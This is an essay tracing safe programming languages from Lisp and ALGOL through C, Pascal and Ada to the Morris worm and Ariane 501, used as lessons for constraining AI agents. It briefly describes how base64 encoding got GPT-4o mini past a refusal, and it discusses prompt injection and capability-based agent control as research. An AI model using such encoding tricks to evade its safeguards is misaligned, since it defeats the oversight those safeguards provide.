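# What the History of Safe Programming Languages Teaches about Enforcing Constraints on AI Systems

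## What a safe language guarantees

A safe programming language makes certain errors impossible in any program written in it. The compiler, which translates source code into machine instructions, enforces part of this guarantee, and checks that run alongside the finished program enforce the rest. Neither depends on the programmer's skill or honesty, so a careful expert and a saboteur work under the same limits. Programmers have had such languages for more than half a century. They still wrote most operating-system kernels, the innermost layer of a computer's software, in C or C++, which lack the guarantee, as *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) notes.

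Some researchers now want limits of the same kind on AI systems, especially on AI agents, which are language models that act by calling software tools or by writing and running code. An agent that reads e-mail or web pages is vulnerable to prompt injection, in which it follows text in the data as if it were an instruction. *Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?* (Williams-King, Oberman and colleagues, 2025) compares this with the memory errors of C. In both cases the attacker may supply any input the system will accept, and the system has no firm boundary between data and commands. The paper argues that decades of work on hardening C and C++ had little success and that changing the language was the better course. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) changes the language an agent uses. The agent must write its actions as programs in a restricted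 form of Scala, and the compiler rejects any program that uses a file or network connection it was not granted.

Whether the analogy helps depends on what the language guarantee consists of, and the guarantee is narrower than the word "safe" suggests.

### One array, two errors

Memory safety is the property that a program only touches memory it is entitled to, within bounds and while that memory is still allocated. Specialists call the bounds half spatial safety and the lifetime half temporal safety. Four lines of C are enough to break both:

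```c
int *a = malloc(10 * sizeof(int));
x = a[10];
free(a);
y = a[0];
```

The first line allocates memory for ten integers, which C numbers from 0 to 9. The second reads an eleventh integer, which does not exist. The third frees the memory, and the fourth still reads from it.

A C compiler typically turns both reads into a plain fetch from an address. For `a[10]`, the address lies just past the array, and x receives whatever is there, perhaps part of a password. After `free`, another part of the program may already have received the same memory, in which case y holds unrelated data. C works this way by design, because its designers wanted a fast language that was easy to implement. *Undefined Behavior in the C Programming Language*, Svoboda's draft for the C standards committee, explains that catching the bad index would require a test at every access and a record of every array's valid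 range.

A bounds-checked language such as Java stores each array's length with the array and checks the index against it at every access. The second line then raises an exception, an error signal that the program either handles or stops on. The last two lines have no counterpart in Java because the programmer cannot free memory. Instead, a garbage collector in the runtime (the software that supports the program while it runs) reclaims a block only when the program can no longer reach it.

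A compile-time checker catches the use of freed memory before the program runs. Rust's compiler tracks which part of a program owns each piece of memory and rejects a program that reads `a` after giving it up. Rixner and Cox's *Unsafe Rust* lists dangling pointers, which point to freed memory, among the errors this analysis makes impossible. The compiler can also catch a literal index of 10 that is out of range for a fixed-size array, but it can't know in advance an index that a user supplies, so Rust uses the same run-time bounds check as Java. O'Reilly's *Unsafe Code* attributes Rust's safety to types, lifetimes and bounds checks together.

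A static check happens before the program runs, and a run-time check happens while it runs. Practical safe languages use both. *Safety and Soundness*, a chapter of the textbook PAPL, reserves the term "statically safe" for languages that check as much as possible beforehand and leave to run time only what no algorithm can settle in advance.

The Java program still contains the programmer's mistake, but the mistake has a predictable outcome. In C, the outcome depends on obscure details such as the layout of memory, which attackers can exploit. *The Meaning of Memory Safety* (Azevedo de Amorim, Hriţcu and Pierce, 2017) draws this contrast, and defines memory safety by what a programmer may conclude about code without reading it rather than by a list of errors. Suppose a program displays pictures with a decoder from a stranger's library. If the decoder is written in a memory-safe language and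 holds no reference to the program's window, it cannot alter the window, however buggy or malicious it is.

They prove this for a small language in which a pointer is a pair (i, n), where i identifies a block of memory and n is a position inside it. Arithmetic on pointers can change n but never i, so code cannot manufacture a pointer to a block that nobody gave it. Write ⟦c⟧(s) for the result of running code c from memory state s, and split the state into s₁, which c can reach, and s₂, which it cannot. If c run on s₁ alone finishes in state s₁′, then

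⟦c⟧(s₁ ∪ s₂) = s₁′ ∪ s₂

up to a renaming of block identifiers. The unreachable memory comes through unchanged, and its contents made no difference to the rest. The proof does assume a memory that never fills up, which no real machine has.

Researchers are still working out how to define memory safety for C itself. Askarov (2026) proposes in *The Downgrading Semantics of Memory Safety* that, roughly, a program is safe if its behaviour does not depend on how the allocator (the routine that hands out memory) works, except where memory runs out or the program explicitly converts a pointer to a number.

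### Undefined behaviour

The C standard has a name for reads like the two above. Undefined behaviour is an operation to which the language assigns no meaning, so that the compiled program may do anything. "Anything" goes well beyond fetching the wrong number, because compilers take advantage of the missing rule. Svoboda gives an example that, for an array of ten, looks like this:

```c
if (i < 0 || i >= 10) y = 0;
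a[i] = 0;
```

The compiler may delete the programmer's test for a bad index. The second line is defined only if i is between 0 and 9, so the compiler can assume that it is and treat the test as redundant. Svoboda describes this as a contract in which the programmer promises to keep i in range and gets faster code in return. If the programmer makes a mistake, the bug often stays hidden during development, because the builds people run in a debugger tend to have fewer of these optimisations.

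An attacker can use such a slip to take control of the machine. An out-of-bounds read discloses data, and an out-of-bounds write changes it. The memory near an array may hold addresses that determine which instructions the processor runs next, so an attacker who controls the index and the value through the program's input can overwrite one of those addresses and divert the program. According to Williams-King and colleagues, attackers usually use a bug to gain the ability to read and write memory at will, then either get the processor to treat their data as code or redirect existing code. In the worst case, they can run commands as though they had logged in. Askarov cites reports from Microsoft and Google that memory errors cause about 70% of security vulnerabilities.

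The C committee is removing what undefined behaviour it can. *Ghosts and Demons* (Uecker, 2026) reports that by August 2026 the committee had voted to remove 45 kinds from the next version of the standard, including a source file that does not end with a newline. Using a bad array index or freed memory is still undefined. Uecker plans to address bad indices with a run-time trap, and freed memory with a memory-safe mode that programmers would have to switch on.

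Klabnik argues in *Memory Safety is a Red Herring* that the real divide between languages is undefined behaviour rather than memory safety. A data race occurs when two threads of a program access the same memory location at once without coordination and at least one of them writes to it. In C++, this makes the behaviour of the entire program undefined. In Java, the program may compute a wrong value, but the specification still rules out some other errors, such as a wrong array length. Klabnik considers a language safe if behaviour is defined by default and the parts where it may not be are clearly marked.

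### Well-typed programs do not "go wrong"

Type safety means that a program never applies an operation to a kind of data the operation isn't defined for. For example, it never adds a number to a truth value. The classic theorem comes from *A Theory of Type Polymorphism in Programming* (Milner, 1978). By then, Milner's type checker for the language ML had been working for nearly two years.

Milner studied a toy language of functions and conditionals. He assigned each expression a mathematical value and added a special value, "wrong", for a failure at run time. Only two things produce it: a conditional whose condition is neither true nor false, and an attempt to apply something that is not a function. A type is in effect a collection of values, and "wrong" belongs to none. The theorem is that if the typing rules give an expression e the type τ, its value ⟦e⟧ belongs to τ:

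e : τ implies ⟦e⟧ ∈ τ, and hence ⟦e⟧ ≠ wrong.

The proof covers each form an expression can take. For example, if e applies f to g, the rules require f to have a type σ → τ and g to have the type σ. Assuming the theorem holds for these smaller expressions, the value of f turns anything in σ into something in τ, and the value of g is in σ, so the result is in τ.

This guarantee leaves out a good deal. An expression that computes forever counts as well behaved, because in Milner's scheme non-termination belongs to every type. A program can also give an incorrect answer without going "wrong" in Milner's sense. The toy language had no memory for a program to alter, and Milner acknowledged that adding one made the theorem harder to prove.

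Wright and Felleisen (1994), in *A Syntactic Approach to Type Soundness*, found a method that copes with alterable memory and with exceptions. They treat a running program as an expression that changes step by step, so that 2 + 3 becomes 5. Failure is now a program that is stuck, neither finished nor covered by any rule for a next step, like 2 + true. The two-part form in today's textbooks came slightly later, and Timany, Krebbers and colleagues (2024), in *A Logical Approach to Type Soundness*, credit it to Robert Harper:

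- Preservation: if e has type τ and e steps to e′, then e′ has type τ.
- Progress: if e has type τ, then e is either finished or can take a step.

A well-typed program therefore stays well typed after each step and never gets stuck. The strength of this guarantee depends on which steps the language defines. In a bounds-checked language, an out-of-bounds `a[10]` has a next step, which is to raise an exception, so the theorem can hold even for programs with bad indices. C defines no next step for such an access. A stray write in C can also replace a number with a value of another type without the type checker detecting it, so type safety in a language with mutable memory requires memory safety.

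### Why a sound checker rejects correct programs

A checker is sound if every program it accepts has the guaranteed property. A checker that rejected everything would be sound, but no checker can be sound and also accept every good program. Suppose a program runs some arbitrary calculation and, if the calculation ever ends, reads the out-of-bounds element `a[10]`. The program is safe exactly when the calculation runs forever. A checker that judged every such program correctly could determine whether any calculation ever stops, and Alan Turing proved that no algorithm can do this. Designers therefore settle for approximation, or require extra rules and annotations from the programmer, as High Assurance Rust's *Static Assurance* explains. A language that promises safety has to err on the side of rejection. The Rust Book's *Unsafe Rust* says it is better to reject some valid programs than to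 accept some invalid ones.

Milner gave an example of a safe program that his own system rejects. A function F takes a function f and a pair (a, b), and returns (f(a), f(b)). Somebody might use F to reverse a list of numbers and a list of words together. This is safe because reversal works on any list, but the checker rejects the program because it requires a and b to have the same type.

Programmers in that position want a way around the checks, and most safe languages have one. An escape hatch is a feature that lets a programmer or user bypass the checks on purpose; Rust's `unsafe` blocks are the best-known example. (A soundness hole, by contrast, is a flaw in a language or its compiler that lets an accepted program break the guarantee.) Timany and colleagues consider escape hatches indispensable, partly because type systems are stricter than necessary and partly because some unchecked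 operations run faster. According to Rixner and Cox, responsibility for the check passes from the compiler to the programmer. Progress and preservation no longer apply to a program that uses an escape hatch. Timany and colleagues have a stronger kind of theorem that can cover unsafe code behind a safe interface, but somebody has to prove that each such piece of code behaves safely.

Programs can also escape a language's checks through a foreign function interface (FFI), which lets code in one language call code in another that the first language cannot check. A Python program that calls a C library is exposed to the library's memory errors. Klabnik points out that if this made Python unsafe, no useful program would count as memory-safe, because every useful program calls the operating system, whose interfaces are not memory-safe. The usual answer is to make an exception for the trusted base,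 which is everything that must be correct for a guarantee to hold, such as the compiler, the runtime and the unchecked library code.

### Limits around an AI system

Developers commonly train a language model further on examples of harmful requests so that it refuses them. The trained model tends to refuse, but not in every case. Williams-King and colleagues asked GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024, what tools would cut down a stop sign, and it declined. When they sent the same question in base64, a way of encoding text as letters and digits, the model no longer refused. Its reply began with "definitely" but was mostly nonsense, because the model was too weak to help.

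An architectural constraint is a limit enforced by the software or hardware around a model and is meant to hold whatever the model outputs. For example, an agent on a computer without a network connection cannot send a file to a stranger, however its training turned out. The Scala system also imposes an architectural constraint. It gives the agent capabilities, which are unforgeable program values that the agent must hold to perform particular actions. Odersky and colleagues accept that hostile text may still influence the model, but they claim that the resulting code cannot use a capability the agent lacks. That claim depends on a trusted base that includes the Scala compiler and the library that defines the capabilities.

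The history of safe languages bears on such constraints through four questions, which apply to a compiler from any decade as much as to the software around an agent:

- Who can step outside the check? Scala programmers ordinarily have unchecked type conversions. Odersky and colleagues forbid these to agents, though the author of a library can still exempt a module by vouching for it.
- Who pays for it? A run-time check costs users some speed. A static check costs programmers time, part of it on code that was correct already.
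- What does it leave uncovered? Writing an agent's runtime in a memory-safe language does not prevent prompt injection, as *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* concedes. *Escaping the Quicksand* (2026) contains a similar forecast for computing at large: fix memory safety, and problems above and below it will soon come to the fore.
- What made people adopt it? A proof was not enough. Milner published his in 1978, and in August 2026 a memory-safe mode for C was still a plan.

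## 1958 to 1991: checked languages exist, and C spreads anyway

John McCarthy began work on the language Lisp at the Massachusetts Institute of Technology (MIT) in 1958. Lisp programs build their data from small linked cells and constantly use up new ones, so McCarthy had the system recover old cells automatically. When free cells run out, the garbage collector follows every link from the data still in use, marks the cells it reaches and reclaims the rest. As in Java, the programmer cannot free memory, so Lisp had the temporal half of memory safety by about 1960. But the program stopped while the collector worked, and according to *Lisp* (Gabriel, 1991), people around 1981 still thought it was impossible to avoid such interruptions on ordinary hardware.

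### The checks that customers kept

Bounds checks followed in 1963, when the British manufacturer Elliott Brothers delivered its compiler for ALGOL 60, an international language for expressing algorithms. Tony Hoare led the compiler's design. In his Turing Award lecture, *The Emperor's Old Clothes*, Hoare (1980) named security as the design's first principle. The compiler had to reject every malformed program, and a program it accepted had to give either a result or an error message that made sense in terms of the source code. Compiled programs therefore checked every array index against the array's upper and lower bounds at every use.

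This slowed programs down. In *Null References*, a talk published in 2009, Hoare recalled that the machine ran fewer than 2,000 operations a second, so the two tests added about a millisecond to each array access. Years after the first delivery, the company asked its customers whether they wanted a switch to turn the checks off in production. They unanimously said no, because they knew how often the checks caught errors in production runs, where an undetected error could be disastrous.

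The story rests on Hoare's memory, and these customers had never worked without the checks. In the 2009 talk he said they had not known that safety could be traded for speed. Users of Fortran, the older scientific language, rejected the checks when Hoare's team built a translator from Fortran to ALGOL. Their programs hit a subscript error within milliseconds of starting, and they wanted the programs to run, so none of them would use the translator. Elliott's own customers valued a check they had seen working, but they objected to one that required extra typing. In October 1963 Hoare passed on their request to relax ALGOL's rule that programs must declare every variable, and the international committee in charge of the language refused.

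Hoare (1973), in *Hints on Programming Language Design*, attacked the common compromise of checking a program during debugging and removing the checks for production. This keeps the checks while nobody relies on the results and removes them when a wrong result may be ruinous. He compared it to a sailor who wears a life jacket for training on dry land and takes it off at sea. He also objected that the debugging and production compilers may not be equally reliable, and that a subtly faulty program may behave differently under each, leaving the programmer with no help in finding the fault. He could accept a loss of speed of 10 or 20 percent, or even 30 or 40, but not a slowdown by a factor of two.

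Elliott ALGOL also let programmers insert machine instructions directly into their source code, an escape hatch that Hoare recommended to other designers. His claim that no program could make the computer "run wild" therefore held only for programs without such instructions.

The American company Burroughs built the array bounds check into the hardware of its B5000 computer, introduced in 1961. A program reached an array through a descriptor, a word of memory holding the array's address and length. According to *Early Descriptor Architectures*, the processor takes the index from a register, compares it with the length in the descriptor, adds it to the address and fetches the word. A contemporary machine at Rice University also stored each array's length but relied on software to check the index against it. Burroughs gave users no assembly language, so they had no ordinary way to bypass the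 descriptors.

The operating system needed more freedom, so Burroughs wrote it in ESPOL, a variant of ALGOL with access to privileged operations. Mayer (1982), in *The Architecture of the Burroughs B5000*, explains how the company kept ordinary programs from using those operations. The system would not run ESPOL code as a normal program, and somebody had to install it as part of the operating system. Only approved compilers could produce executable files, and approving one took a command at the operator's console. In the 1960s, Burroughs was selling a machine that checked array bounds and ran an operating system written in a high-level language.

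The Burroughs design had drawbacks. Later models attached a three-bit tag to every word to distinguish code from data, which took about 6% more memory. The processor needed many components, which could make it less reliable, and it ran Fortran less efficiently than conventional machines did. The protection also depended on Burroughs hardware, so customers could not take it to another manufacturer's computer.

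### Pascal, a language with no way out

Pascal came closer to being a checked language for everyone. Niklaus Wirth designed it for teaching, and by 1981 it dominated computer science courses. Some people also recommended it for operating systems, and a 1977 paper that Hoare co-wrote called it the best language in the public domain for systems programming.

Brian Kernighan disagreed after spending March 1980 to January 1981 rewriting the programs from his book *Software Tools* in Pascal. *Why Pascal is Not My Favorite Programming Language* (Kernighan, 1981) concluded that standard Pascal was a toy, fit for teaching but not for real programming. Kernighan was not neutral, since he worked at Bell Labs, where C originated, and had co-written the best-known book on C. But his complaints are specific enough to check, and he credited Pascal's run-time checks with catching some of his mistakes, especially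 bad array indices.

He considered the treatment of arrays the biggest single problem. Take two declarations:

```pascal
var small : array [1..10] of integer;
    large : array [1..20] of integer;
```

In Pascal the size of an array is part of its type, so `small` and `large` have different types, and no single procedure can sort both. This makes bounds checks simple, because the compiler can always get an array's length from its type. Burroughs kept the length with the data, so one procedure could handle arrays of any size. C passes only the array's address. One C procedure can also sort both arrays, but it works correctly only if the caller supplies the right length.

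Text caused the most trouble, because a Pascal string is an array of characters, and arrays of different lengths, such as 'hello' and 'goodbye', have different types. Kernighan made every string in his programs the same length, long enough for the largest. This would have wasted too much memory in his program for sorting lines of text, so that program stored strings in another form, which needed its own routines for copying and comparing.

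The checks could also stop a program whose author had been careful:

```pascal
while (i <= 10) and (small[i] > 0) do ...
```

The first condition is meant to keep `i` in range, but Pascal did not guarantee that the program would test it first, or skip the second condition if the first failed. When `i` reaches 11, the program may look up `small[11]` anyway and halt with a subscript error.

Kernighan's last complaint, and perhaps the most important in his view, was "There is no escape". Pascal had no equivalent of C's casts, which tell the compiler to treat a value as if it had another type. Programmers therefore could not write a storage allocator in Pascal. An allocator divides raw memory among callers, one of which may store integers in its piece and another names, and Pascal's type system could not describe what such a routine returns. Code that reads from a disk had the same difficulty,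 because the bytes may represent any type of data. Pascal did supply a built-in allocator, but a programmer could not replace it or regain control when it ran out of memory.

Programmers wrote these parts in another language. Kernighan ran his programs on five Pascal systems, four of which were written in C, so the trusted base of Pascal was often a C program.

Pascal's strictness also did not make it fully safe. A variant record is storage that can hold different types at different times, and Kernighan noted that programmers could use one to get a value past the type checker. Some Pascal systems let programmers compile parts of a program separately and did not check that types matched between the parts. These ways around the rules were accidents of the design, and nothing marked their use.

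Vendors responded with extensions. In his 1980 lecture, Hoare had praised Pascal as a small language that could support specialised extensions. Kernighan thought these were a trap, because each group extended Pascal in its own direction and its programs then ran nowhere else. Henriksen (2021), in *There is no escape from Futhark*, observes that later revisions and vendors' extensions fixed most of the major problems. Shah (2017), who had helped to implement a variant of Pascal, replied that some of the criticism applied to particular compilers and not to the language. Neither point solves the problem for somebody choosing a language for an operating system in 1981, who needed an escape hatch that worked the same way on every machine. Elliott and Burroughs had both deliberately provided one, but each only on its own computers.

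### Why C spread

Dennis Ritchie developed C at Bell Labs in the early 1970s, and in 1973 he and Ken Thompson rewrote the Unix operating system in it. Anyone moving Unix to a new computer first needed a C compiler for it, and could then reuse most of the system's code. C spread with Unix, and most Unix programs were written in C.

The compiler was also easy to write. C programmers had to spell out what the machine should do, and Gabriel notes that some people called C a fancy assembly language. Being this explicit made C's speed predictable. In one Lisp program Gabriel describes, an experienced programmer had declared three arrays too vaguely, which made each access about as slow as a function call. Correcting the declarations made the whole system 20% faster. Gabriel thought it almost impossible to write C that performed as badly as some of the Lisp he had seen.

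C also gives direct access to hardware:

```c
*(char *)0xFF00 = 1;
```

This line treats the number FF00 as a memory address and stores a 1 there. That might start the printer on a machine that controls its printer through that address, or corrupt a user's data on another machine. The compiler cannot distinguish these cases, so a language that allows the line everywhere cannot guarantee memory safety.

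Gabriel, a Lisp designer at the software company Lucid, gave the best-known explanation of C's success. He contrasted two schools of design. The MIT school, to which he belonged, wanted the right design even if it was hard to build. The "New Jersey" school, named for the home of Bell Labs, put simplicity of implementation first, a philosophy he called "worse is better".

In his example, a program asks the operating system for a long operation, such as reading a file, and something interrupts it. An MIT designer would have the system restore the program to its earlier state and repeat the request automatically. Unix sometimes returned an error code instead, and a correct program had to check for the code and try again. The Unix designers preferred this because it kept the system simple. C treats array bounds the same way, keeping the compiler simple and requiring the programmer to remember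 the check.

Gabriel argued that a simple system spreads, even if it offers only 50 to 80% of what people want, because it runs acceptably on the half of all computers that are slower or smaller than the median and is easy to move to new ones. Its users get used to sacrificing some safety and convenience for speed. Once enough people depend on it, they improve it until it is nearly right. In 1991 he predicted that by 1995 the world would have a good operating system and a good language, Unix and C++. He admitted to caricaturing the philosophy and was ambivalent about it. In *Worse is Better is Worse*, a reply he wrote under the pseudonym Bourbaki, he called his own article dangerously wrong.

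The explanation fits Lisp well. Around 1981 one major dialect ran only on PDP-10 computers and another only on specially built Lisp machines. By 1987 speed was no longer the obstacle, since Lisp took 0.90, 0.98 and 1.07 times as long as C on three small benchmarks. However, the compiled Lisp was 21 to 48% larger, and the tests did not use a garbage collector that avoids long pauses. The results also came too late to matter much, because by then far more compiler experts were working on C than on Lisp.

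Simplicity of implementation alone does not explain why C spread, because Pascal was simple to implement too. It was a small language, its original compiler read the source code in a single pass, and it ran on machines down to the Z80 microprocessor. Elliott ALGOL also had a simple, compact compiler, and it still checked every index. Unlike standard Pascal, C gave programmers access to the machine and spread along with an operating system.

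Hoare's Fortran story, in which people who were used to unchecked arrays would not accept checks, gives some support to Gabriel's claim about users' expectations. Gabriel's claim that the popular system later becomes nearly right has failed for memory safety, at least in C itself, where an out-of-range index is still undefined behaviour in 2026.

### The Morris worm

On the evening of 2 November 1988, Robert Tappan Morris, a graduate student at Cornell University, released a program that copied itself from computer to computer across the Internet. One of its ways in was finger, a service that told people on other machines who was logged in. The finger server read its request roughly like this:

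```c
char line[512];
gets(line);
```

The C library routine `gets` copies a line of input into memory without checking how much room there is. The worm sent 536 bytes, but `line` had room for only 512. The extra bytes overwrote the address where the program would resume after the current function finished. The program instead jumped to instructions in the worm's message, which opened a command shell for the worm. Any language that checked array bounds would have stopped the copy at the end of `line`.

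Spafford's 2003 retrospective, *A Failure to Learn from the Past*, cites estimates that the worm reached 3,000 to 6,000 machines, or 5 to 10% of the Internet at the time. The worm infected many of them repeatedly, until some could do no further work.

Bounds checks would have stopped the worm's finger attack but not its other methods. It also guessed passwords and exploited lists of computers that trusted one another. The mail program sendmail had a debugging option, often left on, that accepted commands in place of a recipient's address. This confuses data with instructions, as prompt injection does, and a memory-safe language would have allowed it. The finger attack worked only on VAX computers, according to Computer Archeology's *Morris Internet Worm*, although the worm also spread to Sun workstations. Hoare's suggestion in his 2009 talk that there might have been no malware without `gets`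 therefore goes too far. Spafford also mentions a virus that was circulating on Apple II computers in 1981.

Programmers did not abandon C after the worm, partly because the flaws were so easy to fix. A group at Berkeley posted patches for all of them by the next evening. The fix for the finger server was to replace `gets` with `fgets`, which takes the buffer size as an argument. Replacing the language would have meant rewriting Unix, and Hoare had remarked in 1973 that it was almost impossible to persuade a programmer to change languages. Spafford recalls that the public debates that followed were about how to deal with intruders, who was responsible for security and updates, and the future of networks.

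The American standard for C, completed in 1989, kept `gets`, and the standards committee did not remove it until 2011. Spafford counted hundreds of buffer overflows in the fifteen years after the worm, many of them written by programmers who knew the risk. Hoare came to doubt that customers would ask for safer languages unprompted. He compared them to car buyers, who began to demand safety only gradually and with the help of legislation.

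## 1983 to 1997: the United States military requires a safe language

One large customer, the United States Department of Defense, did ask for a safer language. It commissioned Ada and, from 1983, required it for much of its software. Safety was one reason, but the department mainly wanted to stop paying for so many languages. Each armed service had its own, some projects used one that existed nowhere else, and often only the company that had written a system could maintain it. The National Research Council's *Ada and Beyond* (1997), which the department commissioned, repeats a common estimate of at least 450 languages and dialects, though nobody ever made a thorough count. *Programming Language* (1989), by Congress's auditors at the GAO, puts the number in 1974 at over 300.

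In 1975 the department began to draw up requirements for a single language. No existing language met them all, so it held a design competition. The final requirements, called Steelman, came out in 1978, and in 1979 the department chose the design by Jean Ichbiah's team at Cii-Honeywell Bull. The winning language, named Ada, became a military standard in 1980 and an American national standard in 1983. Programmers call the 1983 version Ada 83.

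### Checks with named exits

Steelman called for strict types and for run-time detection of errors such as a bad array index. Ada 83 provides both without the two restrictions on arrays that had frustrated Kernighan in Pascal:

```ada
type Vector is array (Integer range <>) of Integer;
procedure Sort (V : in out Vector);
...
while I <= V'Last and then V (I) > 0 loop
```

The `<>` leaves the length open, so `Sort` accepts an array of any size, and each array carries its bounds, as on the Burroughs machines. With `and then`, the program looks up `V (I)` only if the first condition is true. If a program still uses an index outside an array's bounds, it raises an exception called `Constraint_Error`. Programmers can also declare a number type with a narrow range, such as 0 to 359 for a compass heading, and a value outside the range raises the same exception.

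Ada also has deliberate escape hatches:

- `Unchecked_Conversion` treats the bits of a value as if they belonged to another type.
- `Unchecked_Deallocation` frees a block of memory, even if other pointers to it remain.
- `pragma Suppress` allows the compiler to leave out a particular check, such as the one on array indices, in a chosen part of the program.
- `pragma Interface`, Ada's foreign function interface, declares a routine written in another language.

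These names make it easy to find where a program bypasses the language's safety rules. A reviewer can search for the word "Unchecked", whereas Pascal's variant records had no such marker.

But Ada 83 was not fully memory-safe. The standard permitted a garbage collector, but hardly any compiler supplied one. A program that needed to reuse memory usually had to free it with `Unchecked_Deallocation`, and could then read the freed memory, just as a C program can. Ada 83 also did not reliably catch reads of variables that had not been given a value.

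Steelman required a switch for turning checks off, and noted that suppressing the detection of an error is not an assertion that the error will not occur. Elliott's customers had turned down such a switch in the 1960s.

### Few waivers and a great deal of C

In June 1983 Richard DeLauer, an under secretary of defense, ordered that Ada become the single language for new mission-critical systems, starting in January 1984. Two directives in 1987 extended the rule to nearly all Defense Department software, except where another approved language would cost less over the system's life. Congressional committees still thought the change was too slow. A 1990 law required Ada in all the department's software after 1 June 1991, "where cost effective", unless a designated official granted an exemption.

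A project that wanted to use a language other than Ada needed a waiver, and few asked for one. According to GAO's 1989 report, the Air Force received five requests between 1984 and 1987 and approved them all, while the Army received ten and approved four. The Navy received 43 between 1985 and 1987, and by July 1988 it had approved 23 and denied two, with most of the rest pending. The Navy did not require waivers for its custom-built shipboard and aircraft computers, because no Ada tools for them existed yet. The services also had different rules about when a project needed a waiver. According to GAO's *Programming Language* (1991), one service required a waiver for any code in another language, while another required one only when such code exceeded a set percentage of the program.

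The National Research Council's committee learned of only 31 waivers granted between 1992 and its 1996 study. Yet by 1994, C, which had never been on the Defense Department's list of approved languages, made up 22% of the mission-critical code in conventional high-level languages, compared with 33% for Ada. The committee concluded that many projects had ignored the rule. Route Fifty's *Unlock Ada's grip on DOD, report urges* (1996) adds that no Pentagon official had cracked down on them.

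Most requests for exceptions succeeded, but they went to very senior officials, and many project managers feared that asking would reflect badly on them. So some used Ada where it was a poor choice, and others used another language without asking. The process recorded few of the exceptions actually in use, so the department learned little from it about where Ada worked poorly.

Contractors had practical reasons to want other languages. Ada was hard to compile, and its first production compilers arrived several years after 1980 and were large, slow, unreliable and expensive. When a new processor came out, its first compiler was usually for C, and an Ada compiler was often the last to appear. Companies that sold ready-made components, such as database or windowing software, normally supplied a C interface. An Ada interface might follow months or years later and cost more.

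Some weapons also needed faster responses than early Ada systems could provide. GAO described a helicopter project whose computers had to react in under four milliseconds. Engineers at the Software Engineering Institute, a research centre funded by the department, advised writing such time-critical code in assembly language, which corresponds directly to machine instructions and has no safety checks. Of the 100 Ada projects GAO examined, 69 also used at least one other language, and 44 of those used assembly. GAO did not establish why each project used other languages, but much of the software in Ada projects evidently depended on code outside Ada's guarantee.

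Programmers had a career reason to prefer C or C++ to Ada. The National Research Council's committee looked through job advertisements in two newspapers in 1996 and found that fewer than 3% of the references to languages and tools were to Ada, while C and C++ each accounted for more than 23%.

### One company's records

The department expected Ada to save money, but GAO found in 1989 that no project had set out to measure the savings. The best evidence came from Verdix, a company that made Ada tools and had written its compilers and debuggers partly in C and partly in Ada since 1986. *Comparing Development Costs of C and Ada* (Zeigler, 1995) used the company's records of every change to the code, which developers had classified as new features or fixes.

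This setting allowed an unusually fair comparison because all but two of the 62 developers had worked in both languages, and they used the same design methods, debugger and tests for each.

| | C | Ada |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code, without comments and blanks | 1,508,695 | 1,272,771 |
| Development cost per line | $10.52 | $6.62 |
| Fixes per new feature | 0.52 | 0.25 |
| Bugs found by customers, per 1,000 lines | 0.676 | 0.096 |

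A line of Ada cost 37% less than a line of C, and customers found about one-seventh as many bugs per line. A line of Ada may do less than a line of C, so Zeigler also compared the cost per feature, and found that the company spent $1.63 on a C feature for every dollar it spent on an Ada feature. The recruits' earlier experience does not explain Ada's advantage, since three-quarters of them had done substantial C programming before they joined and fewer than a quarter had done much in Ada.

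The two languages were used for different work, though. The oldest and largest parts of the product were in C, as were 20 of the 25 most expensive directories of code. Among the most expensive directories in each language, the gap narrowed to 0.62 fixes per feature for C and 0.39 for Ada. The company never built the same thing independently in both languages, but it did rewrite its optimiser, the part of a compiler that speeds up the finished program. Customers reported 10 bugs in four years of the Ada version and 31 in four years of the C version, but different people wrote the second version, and they used a new design. Zeigler's employer also sold Ada tools. And the figures count bugs of every kind, so it is impossible to tell from them how much of the difference came from Ada's checks.

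*Detailed Comparisons of Ada and Other Third-Generation Programming Languages*, an appendix to the National Research Council's study, accepted the result for this company but called it only suggestive for others. Its other data were less favourable to Ada on cost. In one private database of 190 projects, military software in C or C++ generally cost no more per line than software in Ada, except for airborne and space weapons, where Ada was cheaper. NASA's Software Engineering Laboratory at first credited Ada with large savings that came from reusing code, but it saw comparable gains when it applied the same approach to Fortran projects. The evidence on defects was more consistent. NASA's Ada programs had 2.1 errors per 1,000 lines, against 4.8 for Fortran. The appendix concluded that Ada software had fewer defects, but that the evidence was too weak to show that it cost less.

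### Flight 501

On 4 June 1996 the first Ariane 5, a European rocket, broke up about 40 seconds after takeoff. The software at fault was written in Ada. The Ariane 501 Inquiry Board's *Ariane 5 Flight 501 Failure* (1996) traces the loss to a single conversion between two kinds of number.

The rocket had two guidance units that measured its position and movement, one active and one on standby. They had identical hardware and ran the same software, nearly all of it from the earlier Ariane 4. One routine aligned the instruments before launch. On Ariane 4 it kept running for about 40 seconds after lift-off. If the countdown stopped in its last seconds, this let the crew restart it without repeating the alignment, which took 45 minutes or more. Ariane 4 crews had used this feature once, in 1989. Ariane 5 had a different launch sequence and did not need it, but the engineers kept it, presumably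 because they were reluctant to change software that worked.

The routine calculated the horizontal bias, which depended on the rocket's horizontal speed. It converted this value from a 64-bit floating-point number to a 16-bit integer, which can hold only values from −32,768 to 32,767. A number outside that range would cause an error. The engineers had looked for this danger and found seven variables at risk. They protected four but left the other three, including the horizontal bias, unprotected because extra code takes processor time and the unit's computer had a maximum workload target of 80%. They reasoned that these three values either had a physical limit or stayed well within the range.

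That held on Ariane 4. Ariane 5 flew a different path and gained horizontal speed much faster, but the project partners had agreed not to include its trajectory in the guidance unit's specification. About 37 seconds into the flight, the horizontal bias no longer fit into 16 bits, and the conversion raised an exception in the standby unit. The active unit failed for the same reason less than a tenth of a second later.

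The specification required a unit to respond to any exception by reporting the failure, saving a record of it and shutting down its processor. The active unit therefore sent a diagnostic pattern instead of flight data. The rocket's main computer read the pattern as flight data and swung the engine nozzles to their limits. The rocket turned more than 20 degrees into the airflow, its boosters tore away, and it destroyed itself as designed.

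The engineers had omitted the protection to save processor time, and the omission remained after their reasoning no longer applied. Reviewers can find uses of `Unchecked_Conversion` by searching for the name, but a missing test leaves no text to search for. The board found no justification for the decision in the source code, and said that the volume of documentation had effectively hidden the assumption from outside reviewers. A ground test with simulated Ariane 5 flight data would have exposed the error, but in 1992 the project had decided to replace the real guidance units with simulated ones in its full-system tests.

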